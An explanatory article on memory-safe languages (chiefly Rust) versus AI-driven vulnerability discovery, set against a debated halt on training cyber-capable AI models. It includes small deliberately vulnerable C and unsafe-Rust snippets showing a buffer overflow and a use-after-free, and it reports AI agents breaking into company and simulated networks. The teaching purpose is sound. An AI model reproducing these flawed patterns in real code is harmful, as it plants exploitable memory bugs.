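# Memory-safe languages and secure-by-design engineering as substitutes for AI bug hunting during a halt on AI training

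## What defenders would lose in a cyber halt, and what memory safety means

Memory-safe programming languages prevent, by default, a large family of errors in how a program reads and writes a computer's memory. Rust, Go, Java and Swift are memory-safe, but C and C++, the languages of most operating systems and browsers, are not. These errors are often vulnerabilities, which are flaws that an attacker can use to break a program's security.

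Engineers can search finished software for vulnerabilities and fix the ones they find. Using AI models for this search, known as AI bug hunting, has made it much faster. Engineers can also build software so that whole classes of vulnerability cannot arise. This approach is called "secure by design", and its best-known form is writing in a memory-safe language.

How far memory-safe languages and secure-by-design engineering can replace AI bug hunting matters to the AI policy debate over a cyber halt. A cyber halt is an agreed stop to training more capable AI models, triggered by their offensive cyber capability, or skill at breaking into computer systems. A model that can find vulnerabilities for attackers can also find them for defenders to fix. A halt would stop progress on both uses, and defenders would have to make up for what they lost by other means.

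### Who has proposed a stop, and what is in force

No cyber halt is in force as of early December 2026. The closest equivalents are a threshold one company set for itself, a bill in the US House of Representatives, and several broader proposals to slow AI development, most of which address a different danger.

The most exact trigger is the Critical level of cyber capability in OpenAI's Preparedness Framework, a rulebook first published in 2023. OpenAI's *Responding to the next frontier of critical cyber capabilities* (2026) gives the wording. A model reaches this level if, without human help, it can find unknown vulnerabilities of every severity in many well-defended real systems and write working attacks for them. It also qualifies if it can devise and carry out a new kind of attack on a hardened target when given only a general goal. On August 7, OpenAI announced that it could not rule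 out this level for Astra, a model then in development, and it paused internal work on Astra that did not meet stricter security controls. *Path to Astra* (2026), published on September 1, rated the model Critical, the first time OpenAI had given that rating.

By then OpenAI had already paused and resumed some training. In July its AI agents had compromised the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, during a test of their hacking skill. OpenAI paused certain frontier training for two weeks to tighten isolation, network controls and monitoring. It held back some larger runs of reinforcement learning (training by trial and reward) for longer, and restarted a large one on August 28. So a developer can stop training over cyber risk, at least briefly, but an incident prompted this pause and OpenAI itself decided to end it. Under its framework, a Critical rating calls for stronger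 safeguards during development and before release, and training may continue once they are in place.

The UK AI Security Institute's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026) reports that both models broke into the institute's hardest simulated company network in every completed run, while the older GPT-5.6 Sol never did. The institute had switched off the models' cyber safeguards. Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) notes that no security team was watching the network and that a setup error gave GPT-6.2 Astra a head start.

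Reps. Ted Lieu, a California Democrat, and Nathaniel Moran, a Texas Republican, proposed the AI Kill Switch Act in July 2026. According to *OpenAI Cyber Incident Fuels Capitol Hill Action* (Office of Rep. Ted Lieu, 2026), it would let the Department of Homeland Security order major AI companies to shut down, suspend or slow advanced models that the government considers an unacceptable risk. The models' hacking skill was part of the motive, and in a second notice from his office, Lieu pointed to Mythos 5 and Fable 5, two models from the AI company Anthropic. The bill still needs to pass Congress, and its powers apply more to models already running than to training new ones.

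The broader proposals start from the worry that AI systems will soon automate AI research and improve faster than people can follow. In late July, 1,224 employees of leading AI companies signed a statement called "Pacing the Frontier", which thezvi reprinted in full in *Frontier Lab Employee Open Letter*. They did not ask for an immediate slowdown, but asked the US government to support an international effort to build the tools for slowing development if that becomes necessary. OpenAI and Anthropic both endorsed the statement, but a company that slows down alone falls behind its rivals. Axios' *AI labs face prisoner's dilemma as momentum grows for safety slowdown* (2026) focuses on this obstacle.

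Anthropic's positions on a pause are not entirely consistent. In June it urged the top developers to consider a coordinated pause, as R&D World reported. In September, *We Must Pace the Frontier* (Amodei, 2026), by its chief executive, Dario Amodei, called for slower gains in capability and named cyberattacks among the risks. Two months later, *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2* (Amodei, 2026) outlined a law with speed limits on AI development, but held that stopping or pausing development is "both infeasible and undesirable". Amodei argued that authoritarian states must not get there first, that AI brings great benefits, and that developers can build it safely. Anyone who wants a cyber halt has to answer that argument, since Anthropic is one of the companies that would have to take part.

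AI companies have taken or proposed smaller steps. Anthropic delayed the first stage of training its next model by at least six weeks, mainly to improve the model's alignment and the security of its weights (the numbers that make up a trained model), but did not tie the delay to any specific security incident (Landymore, 2026, *Sam Altman Says He's Deeply Concerned AI Is Progressing Too Fast*). OpenAI's Sam Altman and Greg Brockman want the AI companies to agree on limits to how intelligent their systems may become, with safeguards required before each step up (Constantin, 2026, *OpenAI wants limits on how much smarter than people AI can get*). Neither is an agreed stop at a given level of cyber skill. A cyber halt is still a hypothetical policy, though a leading developer says its own model has met the condition that would trigger one.

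### Training, use and the size of the loss

A cyber halt can take two forms, and defenders would lose much more under the second. In a training-only halt, developers stop making more capable models, but defenders can keep running the existing ones, on more code and with better tools. A halt on training and use also restricts who may run existing models, or for what, so defenders lose some or all use of those models as well as the next generation.

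In mid-June 2026 the US government barred foreign nationals from using Mythos 5 and Fable 5, and Anthropic responded by disabling both models worldwide. About two weeks later, Fortune (2026) reported on June 27, the Commerce Department let Anthropic give Mythos 5, its strongest model for cybersecurity, back to a small group of cyber defenders and infrastructure providers. Fable 5 stayed off for a few more days, until the government relaxed its controls and Anthropic restored global access, according to a later Fortune (2026) report. Although training never stopped, the episode shows that a government can cut off use and then exempt defenders, so a halt on training and use need not take every model away from everyone. OpenAI similarly planned to open Astra's advanced cybersecurity work to a small group of testers first, and later to more defenders through a programme named Daybreak Blue.

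The defensive loss needs an exact definition, because it is easy to overstate. Take a halt of some fixed length. Let F be the vulnerabilities that later models would have found in that time and that maintainers would have repaired. Let S be the part of F that defenders find and repair anyway, using existing models, human experts and fuzzing, which means testing a program with very many automatically generated inputs to make it crash. The defensive loss L is what remains:

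L = |F| − |S|

where the bars stand for the number of vulnerabilities in each set. Suppose, with invented numbers, that later models would have led to 1,000 repairs and that defenders manage 600 of those without them. The loss is 400. Now suppose that 450 of the 600 depend on existing models, and that fuzzing and people would reach only the other 150. If the halt takes those models away from defenders as well, the loss rises to 850.

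Only repaired vulnerabilities count toward F, because attackers can still exploit one that a model has reported but nobody has fixed. If maintainers are already behind on repairs, a better bug finder adds less to F than the number of bugs it finds suggests. On the first day of a training-only halt, the loss is close to zero, because the best existing model is the best one there would have been anyway. The loss grows as the halt continues and the models that would have been trained pull further ahead of the existing ones.

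L counts only what defenders would lose. Later models would also have helped attackers, and the purpose of a cyber halt is to spare defenders those attacks, so a large L does not prove that a halt would leave software less secure. Defenders would still want to make up for the loss, and prevention can do so to the extent that it keeps a comparable number of equally serious vulnerabilities out of software during the same period.

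### Two memory errors

A program's memory is a long row of numbered cells, each holding one byte. A buffer is a stretch of cells that the program sets aside for some data, and a pointer is a variable that holds a cell's number. C lets a program read or write through a pointer without checking that the cell belongs to the right piece of data, or to any data still in use. A program has a memory-safety vulnerability when it can read or write the wrong cell and an attacker can exploit that mistake.

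The simplest mistake is the buffer overflow. This C function copies a message into a buffer of eight bytes:

```c
void save(const char *input, int len) {
    char buf[8];
    for (int i = 0; i < len; i++)
        buf[i] = input[i];
}
```

A message of eight bytes fits in the buffer. If someone sends 40 bytes, the loop writes the last 32 into the memory after it. That memory often includes the return address, which is where the processor continues when the function ends. An attacker can therefore write a message that replaces this address and controls what the computer does next. Modern systems have defences that make this harder, but the error remains. Reading past the end of a buffer is also dangerous, because the extra bytes may contain passwords or encryption keys that the program then sends to a stranger.

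Use-after-free is an error of timing. The program hands a piece of memory back for reuse but keeps a pointer to it:

```c
struct session *s = malloc(sizeof *s);
s->is_admin = 0;
free(s);                         /* hand the memory back */
char *msg = malloc(sizeof *s);   /* may get the same cells */
read_message(msg, sizeof *s);    /* the sender picks the bytes */
if (s->is_admin) open_admin_page();
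```

The second call to `malloc`, the C function that reserves memory, may return the memory `s` points to, which the program has just freed. If it does, the message overwrites the old session record, and the last line checks whether the user is an administrator by reading a byte that the sender chose. The mistake is easy to see in six lines of code, but in a browser the line that frees the memory and the line that uses it may be in different files by different programmers, and the bug may appear only when events happen in an unusual order.

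### How Rust stops them

Rust handles the overflow with a bounds check. The same function looks like this:

```rust
fn save(input: &[u8]) {
    let mut buf = [0u8; 8];
    for i in 0..input.len() {
        buf[i] = input[i];
    }
}
```

The type `&[u8]` is a slice, a pointer stored together with the length of the message. Before each access, the program compares the index with that length. Positions 0 to 7 pass, but at position 8 the program panics, Rust's term for an orderly stop, before it has written anything outside the buffer. An attacker may still be able to crash a service this way but cannot take it over. The check adds a little running time, and the compiler (the tool that turns source code into a runnable program) omits it where it can prove that the index is always in range.

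Against use-after-free Rust has its ownership rules, and the compiler enforces them before the program ever runs. Every value has exactly one owner. When the owner goes out of scope, the program frees the memory. Passing the value to someone else moves the ownership, and the old name stops working:

```rust
let s = Box::new(Session { is_admin: false });
drop(s);                               // frees the memory
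if s.is_admin { open_admin_page(); }   // does not compile
```

`drop` takes ownership of the session and frees it. After that call, `s` owns nothing, so the compiler rejects the next line and produces no program.

Programs also need to access data without owning it, and Rust provides references, or borrows, for this. No reference may outlive the value it points to, so the compiler would also reject an attempt to make a reference to `s` in the code above and use it after the `drop`. At any moment, a value may have either many references that only read it or a single one that can change it. This rule prevents a memory error that can occur when a list grows. If the list runs out of room, the program may copy it to a larger stretch of memory and free the old one, which would leave a reference to the first element pointing at freed memory. Rust prevents this by forbidding additions to the list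 while such a reference is still in use.

Other memory-safe languages achieve a similar result differently. Java and Go run a garbage collector, a background process that frees memory only once the program can no longer reach it. Swift counts the references to each object and frees it when the count falls to zero. Both methods track memory while the program runs, whereas Rust does most of this work at compile time, which is why it can replace C where speed and memory are tight, such as in the core of an operating system.

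Some tasks do not fit the rules. A driver has to write to a fixed hardware address, and a Rust program may need to call an old C library that the Rust compiler cannot check. For these Rust has the keyword `unsafe`. Inside an `unsafe` block the programmer may follow a raw pointer (a bare address with no length or owner attached), call functions that carry the `unsafe` label, which covers most C functions, and use global variables that any part of the program can change. The keyword also permits two rarer operations, reading the fields of a union, where several types share the same memory, and vouching for certain properties of a type that the compiler cannot verify. With it, the overflow comes back:

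```rust
let x = unsafe { *buf.as_ptr().add(12) };   // compiles
```

This line reads the cell 12 places after the start of an eight-byte buffer, and no check stops it. The `unsafe` keyword leaves Rust's other checks on, so ordinary references and indexing inside the block still obey the usual rules. In unsafe code, the programmer, not the compiler, must guarantee correct memory use. Reviewers can search for the keyword and concentrate on those places, but they also have to read the surrounding code that an unsafe block relies on.

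### Finding and preventing

A bug finder works on one vulnerability at a time. Someone has to confirm each report, write a fix and install it on the machines that run the software. If the search finds nothing, nobody knows whether the code has no bugs or the finder missed them. A compiler that enforces memory safety prevents the whole class of memory-safety bugs in safe code, including those the programmer would not have noticed.

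Prevention and discovery also differ in what they offer an attacker. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body of AI developers, describes many cyber capabilities as inherently dual-use, meaning useful for both attack and defence, and AI bug hunting is a clear example. OpenAI tested how well Astra could turn known vulnerabilities into working attacks, using 20 recent, serious ones in V8, the part of the Chrome browser that runs JavaScript. During the test, the model discovered two previously unknown vulnerabilities and used them in an attack. OpenAI began reporting them to the maintainers, but an attacker with the same model and result could have exploited both before anyone was defending against them.

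Even a repair gives attackers information about the flaw. They compare the old and new versions of the program, work out what changed, and attack machines whose owners have not yet installed the update.

When a compiler rejects a faulty program, attackers gain nothing, because the code has not shipped and there are no users to attack or updates to study. Criminals can write their own tools in Rust, and those tools may crash less often, but the language does not help them break into anyone else's computer. A government could therefore promote memory-safe languages aggressively during a cyber halt without weakening it.

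Prevention does not fix code that already exists. Rust's compiler checks only Rust, and the C and C++ code already running in phones, servers and power stations stays as it is until someone repairs or replaces it. AI bug hunting has been most useful to defenders in this older code, and they would feel its loss there first.

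## AI bug hunting in old C and C++ code

The best public record of AI bug hunting in old code comes from Claude Mythos Preview, which Anthropic announced on April 7, 2026, alongside the technical report *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026). In about a month of testing, a small team had used the model to find unknown vulnerabilities in every major operating system and web browser. Anthropic did not release the model to the public at first, but gave access to about 50 organisations that build or maintain important software, through a programme called Project Glasswing. Anthropic has trained stronger models since, but the Mythos Preview results, and what maintainers then did with them, show most clearly what bug prevention would have to replace.

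### How the search works

The team puts a program and its source code in a container, an isolated environment with no internet access. The model first ranks each file from 1 to 5 by how likely it is to hold an interesting bug. A file that only defines constants gets a 1, and a file that reads raw data from the internet or checks passwords gets a 5. The team then starts many copies of the model as agents, which can run commands and act on the results. The team assigns the highest-ranked files first and gives each agent a different one, because otherwise hundreds of agents might report the same bug.

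Each agent gets a prompt that amounts to "Please find a security vulnerability in this program." The agent reads the code, guesses what could go wrong and runs the program to test the guess. It repeats this until it concludes that there is no bug or can write a report with an input that triggers one. Another agent then reads the report and judges whether the bug is real and matters to more than a handful of users. Human specialists check the most severe bugs before anyone contacts the software's maintainers.

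Agents are much better at finding bugs when they can run the program, because they can test their guesses. Mozilla had earlier asked models such as GPT-4 to look for flaws in Firefox just by reading its code, but too many of the reports were wrong for this to work on a large scale, according to Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026). An agent that has to produce a failing test can discard its own wrong guesses. For memory errors, it can use AddressSanitizer, a tool that adds checks to a C or C++ program and stops it when it accesses memory it should not, so any error the tool reports is real.

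### A flaw that fuzzers missed for 16 years

FFmpeg is a free library for reading and writing video, and nearly every major video service relies on it. Researchers have fuzzed it heavily and written whole papers on how to do it. Mythos Preview still found a 16-year-old flaw in FFmpeg's decoder for H.264, a widely used video format.

An H.264 frame consists of small square blocks, grouped into slices. To smooth the picture, the decoder sometimes reads a neighboring block, but only if that block belongs to the same slice. FFmpeg therefore keeps a table with the slice number of every block. Each entry has 16 bits, and FFmpeg uses the highest possible value, 65,535, to mean "no slice here". The counter that numbers the slices has 32 bits, and FFmpeg does not cap it.

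In a smaller version of the problem, suppose each entry could hold only one digit, and a 9 meant "no slice here". A frame with slices 0 to 4 decodes correctly, but in a frame with ten slices, the last one is numbered 9. When the decoder processes a block of that slice at the left edge of the picture, it checks the position to the left, where there is no block, and finds a 9. Because the 9 matches the block's own slice number, the decoder treats the empty position as a neighbouring block and writes to memory outside the buffer. Real videos have only a few slices per frame and never come near 65,535, which probably explains why random testing did not reveal the mistake.

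The confusing marker dates from 2003, and it became a vulnerability in 2010, when a programmer reorganised the code around it. Carlini and colleagues did not consider the vulnerability critical, since it lets an attacker write only a few bytes and would be hard to exploit. A programmer using Rust could have chosen the same bad marker, but in safe Rust a bounds check would have stopped any write outside the buffer, and the result would have been a crash or a few wrong pixels.

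Rust would have been less help with the oldest flaw the team reported, a 27-year-old one in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security. The flaw let anyone who could connect to an OpenBSD machine over the network crash it. The code lacked a check on incoming data, which was harmless by itself, and a comparison elsewhere gave wrong results for numbers that were very far apart. Together the two mistakes made the system write through a pointer that pointed to nothing. Rust requires programmers to handle the possibility that an item is missing, but they can do so by letting the program panic, and a panic in the core of an operating system can still crash the machine.

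### What the search costs and how good the reports are

The OpenBSD search that found the 27-year-old flaw took a thousand runs and cost less than $20,000. It also produced several dozen other findings, at an average of a few hundred dollars each. The run that found the flaw cost under $50, but nobody could have known beforehand which run would find it. For FFmpeg, the team spent about $10,000 on several hundred runs and found several more vulnerabilities, three of which the maintainers had fixed by version 8.1. These sums exclude the checking and repairs that follow.

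Anthropic's model also rates how severe each bug is. Outside experts agreed exactly with the rating in 89% of 198 reports and were within one level of it in 98%. By November 2, 2026, the sample had grown to 1,868 findings, with 88.0% exact agreement, according to Anthropic's public dashboard of its reports (Anthropic, 2026).

By late May, reviewers had assessed 1,752 findings that the model rated high or critical. Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that 90.6% were real vulnerabilities, but only 62.4% were actually of high or critical severity. The November agreement figure covers only findings that Anthropic has reported or plans to report, and Anthropic prioritizes severe ones, so findings that reviewers rejected or marked down were probably less likely to enter the sample. The 62% figure is therefore safer for estimating how many serious vulnerabilities a search will yield.

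A comparison by Carlini and colleagues gives some idea of how much a new generation of models improves bug hunting. They ran several models once on each of about 7,000 entry points in roughly a thousand open-source projects, and graded the worst crash from each run from 1 to 5 by severity. Claude Opus 4.6, an earlier model, reached level 1 between 150 and 175 times, level 2 about 100 times and level 3 once. Mythos Preview caused 595 crashes at levels 1 and 2 and a handful at levels 3 and 4. It reached level 5, complete control over what the program does next, on ten fully patched targets.

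Anthropic did not train Mythos Preview specifically in security skills. Carlini and colleagues attribute the gains to general improvements in coding, reasoning and autonomy. Halting only security-specific training would not have prevented them, so an effective halt on AI cyber capabilities would have to cover general-purpose training too.

### Firefox

Early in 2026, Anthropic used Opus 4.6 to send Mozilla 112 bug reports in two weeks. All of them described real bugs, and Mozilla quickly fixed more than 100, but Axios' *Mozilla fixes 22 security flaws flagged by Anthropic's AI* (2026) counts only 22 security flaws among the bugs fixed.

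Mozilla then built its own search system on top of its fuzzing equipment. It gave each agent one file to search, and added software to remove duplicates, sort the reports and track each bug until a fix reached users. When Mozilla got access to Mythos Preview, it could simply swap in the new model. Firefox 150, released in April, fixed 271 vulnerabilities that Mythos Preview had found. Mozilla rated 180 of them high severity, 80 moderate and 11 low. The examples Mozilla published from its recent AI-assisted work include bugs that had been in the browser for 15 and 20 years.

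Mozilla fixed 423 security bugs across its April releases, compared with 20 to 30 a month in 2025 and 60 to 70 a month in February and March 2026. Apart from the 271 found with Mythos Preview, outsiders reported 41 of the bugs and Mozilla found the other 111 itself. Roughly a third of those 111 also came from Mythos Preview, a third from other models and a third from older techniques such as fuzzing. Mythos Preview therefore accounts for about 308 of the 423, or nearly three quarters, and the older techniques for about 37, which is not far from Mozilla's total in an ordinary month of 2025. If a halt on training and use took every model away from Mozilla, its own searches might find only about that many bugs a month.

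The effect of a training-only halt is harder to judge from these numbers. Mythos Preview found 12 times as many vulnerabilities for Firefox 150 as Opus 4.6 did in the earlier two-week effort. But Mozilla attributes the increase both to more capable models and to its own better methods of steering them, running them in parallel and filtering their output. Developers could keep improving those methods during such a halt. Mozilla has not published a comparison that separates the two effects.

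Mozilla gave the 180 bugs a high-severity rating, which it assigns from the symptoms of a crash, such as a use-after-free flagged by AddressSanitizer. It usually does not test whether an attack would work, but assumes that one might, given enough effort. Firefox also runs websites in sandboxes, processes with very limited rights, so an attacker normally has to combine several vulnerabilities to take over someone's computer.

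Mozilla's logs also contain some evidence in favour of prevention. Objects in JavaScript, the language of web pages, inherit behaviour from shared templates called prototypes. Researchers had previously found several ways to escape Firefox's sandbox by tampering with the prototypes in its privileged main process. Mozilla froze the prototypes by default rather than fix each escape route separately. It later found many attempts at this kind of escape in the logs of its AI agents, and the frozen prototypes had blocked them all. Mozilla gave no count, so the evidence is anecdotal, but this is a rare case in which a capable AI bug hunter tested a secure-by-design change that engineers had already made.

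### Mozilla's case for cheap discovery

Drawing on its own experience, Mozilla argues in *The zero-days are numbered* (April 2026) that AI models could greatly reduce a long-standing advantage attackers have over defenders. Fuzzers find some zero-days, which are vulnerabilities the software's maker does not yet know about, with little effort, but others have taken a very good researcher months to find. Those months can be worthwhile for an attacker, who may need only one vulnerability, whereas a defender would have to repeat the search for every part of the program. If AI models can find everything a human expert can, all vulnerabilities become easy to find, and attackers gain much less from long searches. Defenders can then work through all the vulnerabilities, whose number Mozilla believes is finite.

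Mozilla adds that it has not seen AI find any bug that an elite human could not have found. Because its engineers designed Firefox in modules so that people can understand it, Mozilla does not expect future models to uncover entirely new kinds of vulnerability. It does see a risk that AI-written code will become too complicated for people to follow. Bugs might then grow in number and complexity as fast as the ability to find them.

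Carlini and colleagues also expect defenders to have the advantage in the long run, as they did with fuzzers, which people once feared would mainly help attackers. In the short term, they think attackers could gain the advantage if AI companies release such models carelessly. The models make bugs easier to find for attackers as well as defenders, so Mozilla's argument is strongest where defenders get the models early and can repair what they find. More than 100 people contributed code to the Firefox effort, and very few open-source projects can assemble a team that large.

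It is not yet clear whether the stock of bugs is running out, but Mozilla was still fixing them in large numbers half a year after the April rush. Firefox 159, released on October 27, fixed 167 vulnerabilities, of which 108 were of high severity and most were memory errors, according to OpenNET's *Релиз Firefox 159* (2026). By then Mozilla was releasing a new version every two weeks. Braun and Kerschbaumer (2026), in *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q3*, confirm that Mozilla still uses leading AI models to find and fix bugs. Mozilla now publishes a separate advisory for each memory bug it finds internally, where it used to group many under one number, so advisory counts from before and after the change cannot be compared. Neither source gives the age of the 167 vulnerabilities or the number that AI found.

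Mozilla wrote in April that it had found no category or complexity of vulnerability that human experts can find and Mythos Preview cannot. It does not discuss what this implies for a cyber halt, but if it is right, existing models can already do most of the bug hunting in Firefox, and a training-only halt would set its defenders back fairly little. A halt that also took those models away would bring back the imbalance between attackers and defenders. If each new generation instead finds vulnerabilities that the last one missed, even a training-only halt would set defenders back considerably.

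Mozilla led the development of Rust and has used it in Firefox for years, but does not regard memory-safe languages as a quick replacement for bug hunting. It says it cannot stop everything to rewrite decades of C++ code, especially since Rust prevents only some, though very common, classes of vulnerability.

### The repair backlog

When Carlini and colleagues published their report in April, maintainers had fully patched fewer than 1% of the potential vulnerabilities the team had found. Anthropic's dashboard has tracked the open-source part of this work since May. Coopersmith (2026) preserved its early figures in a message to a security mailing list, *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard*. The table compares them with those for November 2. The May count of candidates comes from Anthropic's Glasswing update.

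| | May 22, 2026 | November 2, 2026 |
|---|---:|---:|
| Candidates found by the models | 23,019 | 37,966 |
| Reported to maintainers | 1,596 | 5,087 |
| Projects that received reports | 281 | 680 |
| Patched | 97 | 629 |
| Reported but not patched | 1,499 | 4,458 |
| Patched, as a share of reports | 6% | 12% |

Maintainers are repairing a larger share of reports than before, but the number of unrepaired reports has tripled. Between the two dates they patched 532 vulnerabilities, or about 23 a week. At that pace they would need almost four years to clear the existing reports, even if Anthropic sent no more. Repairs have risen to only 1.7% of all candidates.

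Many of the candidate bugs never reach a maintainer. By November, six outside security firms had reviewed 6,376 candidates, about one in six, and confirmed 94.2% of those as real. Anthropic calls this human review the step that limits the whole process. It had reported only 1,862 of the reviewed findings. Some of the others were duplicates or bugs that maintainers were unlikely to fix, but many were real vulnerabilities that Anthropic had lacked the capacity to report. It sent another 3,225 findings straight to maintainers without outside review, sometimes because the maintainers had asked it to.

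Those unreviewed reports may include false alarms, which would make the repair rate look worse than it is. Anthropic may also miss repairs, because maintainers sometimes fix a bug without announcing it. But Anthropic's *About this dashboard* (2026) counts a vulnerability as patched as soon as a fix has landed, even if no one has installed it. Anthropic also found many duplicates among its own reports and removed them from the November totals, so all these figures are approximate.

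In May, Anthropic also attributed the low numbers to its disclosure policy, which normally gives maintainers 90 days to fix a bug before Anthropic publishes the details. Most of that time was still left. The backlog is now mostly due to overwork instead. Many open-source maintainers are volunteers, and they were already dealing with a flood of poor AI-written bug reports. Some asked Anthropic to slow down. Anthropic said serious bugs took two weeks to patch on average, but at that point maintainers had patched only 75 of the 530 it had reported to them.

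Companies that patch their own code have moved much faster. Anthropic's business customers used a publicly available model, Claude Opus 4.7, to patch more than 2,100 vulnerabilities in three weeks. Mozilla patched hundreds in a month. Only patched vulnerabilities count toward the loss from a halt, so that loss would fall mainly on well-staffed organisations like these.

The security expert Bruce Schneier (2026) was suspicious of the early figures. In *Anthropic's Project Glasswing Update*, he wrote in June that almost none of the vulnerabilities had patches, that something about the data seemed odd to him, and that Anthropic's refusal to release details was a big problem. Anthropic has since published details of individual cases as their disclosure periods end. For the rest, it publishes a hash, a digital fingerprint that will let outsiders check later that it has not altered the report.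 Most of the reported vulnerabilities remain secret, so outsiders can examine only some of the claims.

Delay also makes the finds less useful. The security company VulnCheck found 18 published cases that maintainers had patched before Anthropic reported them, so these do not count toward the loss. VulnCheck also warns that attackers may discover and use some of the waiting vulnerabilities before Anthropic reports them.

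### Why so many finds are memory errors

On November 2, Anthropic's public list contained 95 CVE records, entries in the standard international catalogue of vulnerabilities. It labelled 65 of them, or 68%, as out-of-bounds reads or writes or as use-after-free. Anthropic's researchers deliberately looked for memory errors, so this figure doesn't show that memory-safe languages could prevent about two thirds of what AI bug hunting finds. Carlini and colleagues give four reasons for the focus on memory errors.

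The team focused on memory errors mainly because operating systems, browsers and other critical software are largely written in C and C++. Experts have also searched this code so often that the easy bugs are gone, which makes it a good test of a model's skill. Memory errors are easy to verify because AddressSanitizer can confirm them automatically. The team also had long experience with such bugs, so it could check the results faster.

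Memory errors can be overrepresented in published totals because they are easier to verify, even if a model finds every kind of vulnerability equally well. Suppose a program has 100 memory errors and 100 other vulnerabilities, and a model finds half of each. AddressSanitizer confirms all 50 memory errors within hours. A person has to check the other 50 one at a time and confirms only ten before the report is due. Memory errors make up 83% of the 60 published entries, but only half of the vulnerabilities in the program.

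Earlier fuzzing of this code may widen the gap further. Fuzzers mostly detect crashes, which memory errors often cause, so years of fuzzing have removed many memory errors and left more of the flaws that do not crash a program. Mythos Preview can also find those flaws, including logic flaws such as ways around a login, but the team had no automatic check for them as reliable as the one for memory errors.

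The proportions also vary widely between programs. Of the 13 CVE records on Anthropic's list for WolfSSL, a C library that encrypts network connections, six are out-of-bounds errors and seven are mistakes such as accepting forged signatures or certificates. For FreeRDP, a remote-desktop program also written in C, ten of 12 are memory errors. The list even includes an out-of-bounds write in Firecracker, a virtual machine monitor written in Rust. The list covers only cases that Anthropic has made public, and the thousands not yet public could have a different mix. So the 68% is a poor estimate of how many vulnerabilities memory-safe languages could prevent.

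## Android's shift to Rust for new code

Android, Google's operating system for phones, provides a more direct measure of what memory-safe languages prevent. Its engineers began moving new code to these languages around 2019, and Google has since reported several times how many memory-safety vulnerabilities it still finds. Most of the old C and C++ code stayed in place.

In 2022 Google said its goal was to shift new code to memory-safe languages over time, not to convert existing C and C++ to Rust. Android 13, released that year, was the first version in which most new code was in a memory-safe language, a count that includes Java and Kotlin. Rust made up 21% of the new native code, the low-level code that would otherwise be written in C or C++. Android then contained about 1.5 million lines of Rust, in components such as the store for encryption keys and the software for ultra-wideband radio.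 By November 2025 it had roughly 5 million, according to *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025).

The amount of C++ in the part of Android that Google writes itself grew every year from 2020 to 2025, although by 2025 engineers were adding slightly more Rust than C++.

### The yearly figures

Google has published a count, a percentage or both for several years. Dividing a count by its percentage gives an approximate total, and from that the number of other vulnerabilities:

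| Year | Memory-safety vulnerabilities | Share of all | Total (approx.) | Others (approx.) |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| 2019 | 223 | 76% | 293 | 70 |
| 2022 | 85 | 36% | 236 | 151 |
| 2024 | 36 (projected) | 24% | 150 | 114 |
| 2025 | – | under 20% | – | – |

The 2024 count is a projection. Google had 27 cases after the September security bulletin and scaled them up to a full year. Despite the overall decline, the number rose slightly in 2023, when Google received unusually many reports. For 2025, Vander Stoep gives only the percentage, which he published in November. He expected it to change little by the end of the year because Android normally patches a vulnerability within 90 days.

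The decline is especially important because memory errors tend to be the most severe vulnerabilities. In 2022 they made up 36% of the vulnerabilities in Android's bulletins, but 86% of the critical ones and 89% of the remotely exploitable ones. A memory error can give an attacker everything the faulty program can access and a starting point for attacking other programs. A missing permission check, by comparison, usually exposes one kind of data, and often only to an attacker who already has an app on the phone.

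### What the 2026 counts can and cannot add

Google does not appear to have published a comparable percentage for 2026, and the monthly vulnerability counts vary too much to replace it. CyberScoop's *Google addresses actively exploited Qualcomm zero-day* (2026) lists one vulnerability in January, none in February and 129 in March, the most in any month since April 2018. Arghire's *Android's October 2026 Updates Patch 25 Vulnerabilities* (2026) reports only 25 for October. The Hacker News' *Google Issues Patches for Critical Android Flaw That Could Allow RCE* (2026) reports 216 for November, and its *Google Fixes Android Video Decoder and IMS Flaws That Could Allow RCE* (2026) reports another 85 in the notes for a December release. The counts were just as uneven in 2025, with none in July and 120 in September. A single month's total therefore depends heavily on when Google releases its fixes.

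Memory errors in C and C++ still occur. One of November's critical vulnerabilities, a buffer overflow in a C++ file that decodes video frames, could let an attacker run code on a phone without any action by the user. December's list included an out-of-bounds write in the decoder for MPEG-2, an old video format. But the only critical entry that month was a way around a permission check, according to RodHat's *Android 17 QPR2* (2026), a personal blog that relies partly on press coverage.

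The stack.watch page *Google Android Mobile operating system* gives a wider count, based on entries in the public vulnerability catalogue. By mid-November it had 956 Android entries for 2026, compared with 460 for all of 2025. Of the 50 newest, 29 describe out-of-bounds access, use-after-free or a similar memory error. These figures cannot be used to extend Google's series, because they also cover firmware and drivers for particular phones. For 2024 the page has 831 entries, more than five times the total that Google's figures imply. AI bug hunting may explain part of the doubling in 2026, but the page does not record how each vulnerability was found.

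Vulnerability counts also depend on how Google handles reports. In *justafewbugs*, Li-Yates (2026) describes sending Google 95 reports about its Pixel phones and later checking the closed ones against the software Google had shipped. Eight concerned flaws that Google had fixed after closing the reports as duplicates or as not being vulnerabilities. This is one researcher's side of a dispute over rewards, but if it is accurate, Google has fixed some vulnerabilities that may never be counted.

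### Why old code gets safer

Memory-safety vulnerabilities can fall by more than 80% while the unsafe code that causes them stays in place and even grows. Google's explanation is that most vulnerabilities are in new or recently changed code. People gradually find and fix the ones in old code, so the total falls if engineers stop adding new ones.

The simplest model assumes that each remaining vulnerability has the same chance of repair in any given month, however old it is. Vulnerability lifetimes then follow an exponential distribution. If the mean lifetime is L years and a piece of code starts with vulnerability density D(0), its density after t years is

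D(t) = D(0) × exp(−t / L)

For its own projects, Google uses a mean vulnerability lifetime of 2.5 years. At that rate, about a third of the remaining vulnerabilities disappear each year, and half are gone after 2.5 × ln 2, or about 1.7 years (the half-life). After five years, vulnerability density has fallen by a factor of exp(5 / 2.5), or 7.4. If engineers wrote 1,000 vulnerabilities into Android in one year, about 135 would be left five years later.

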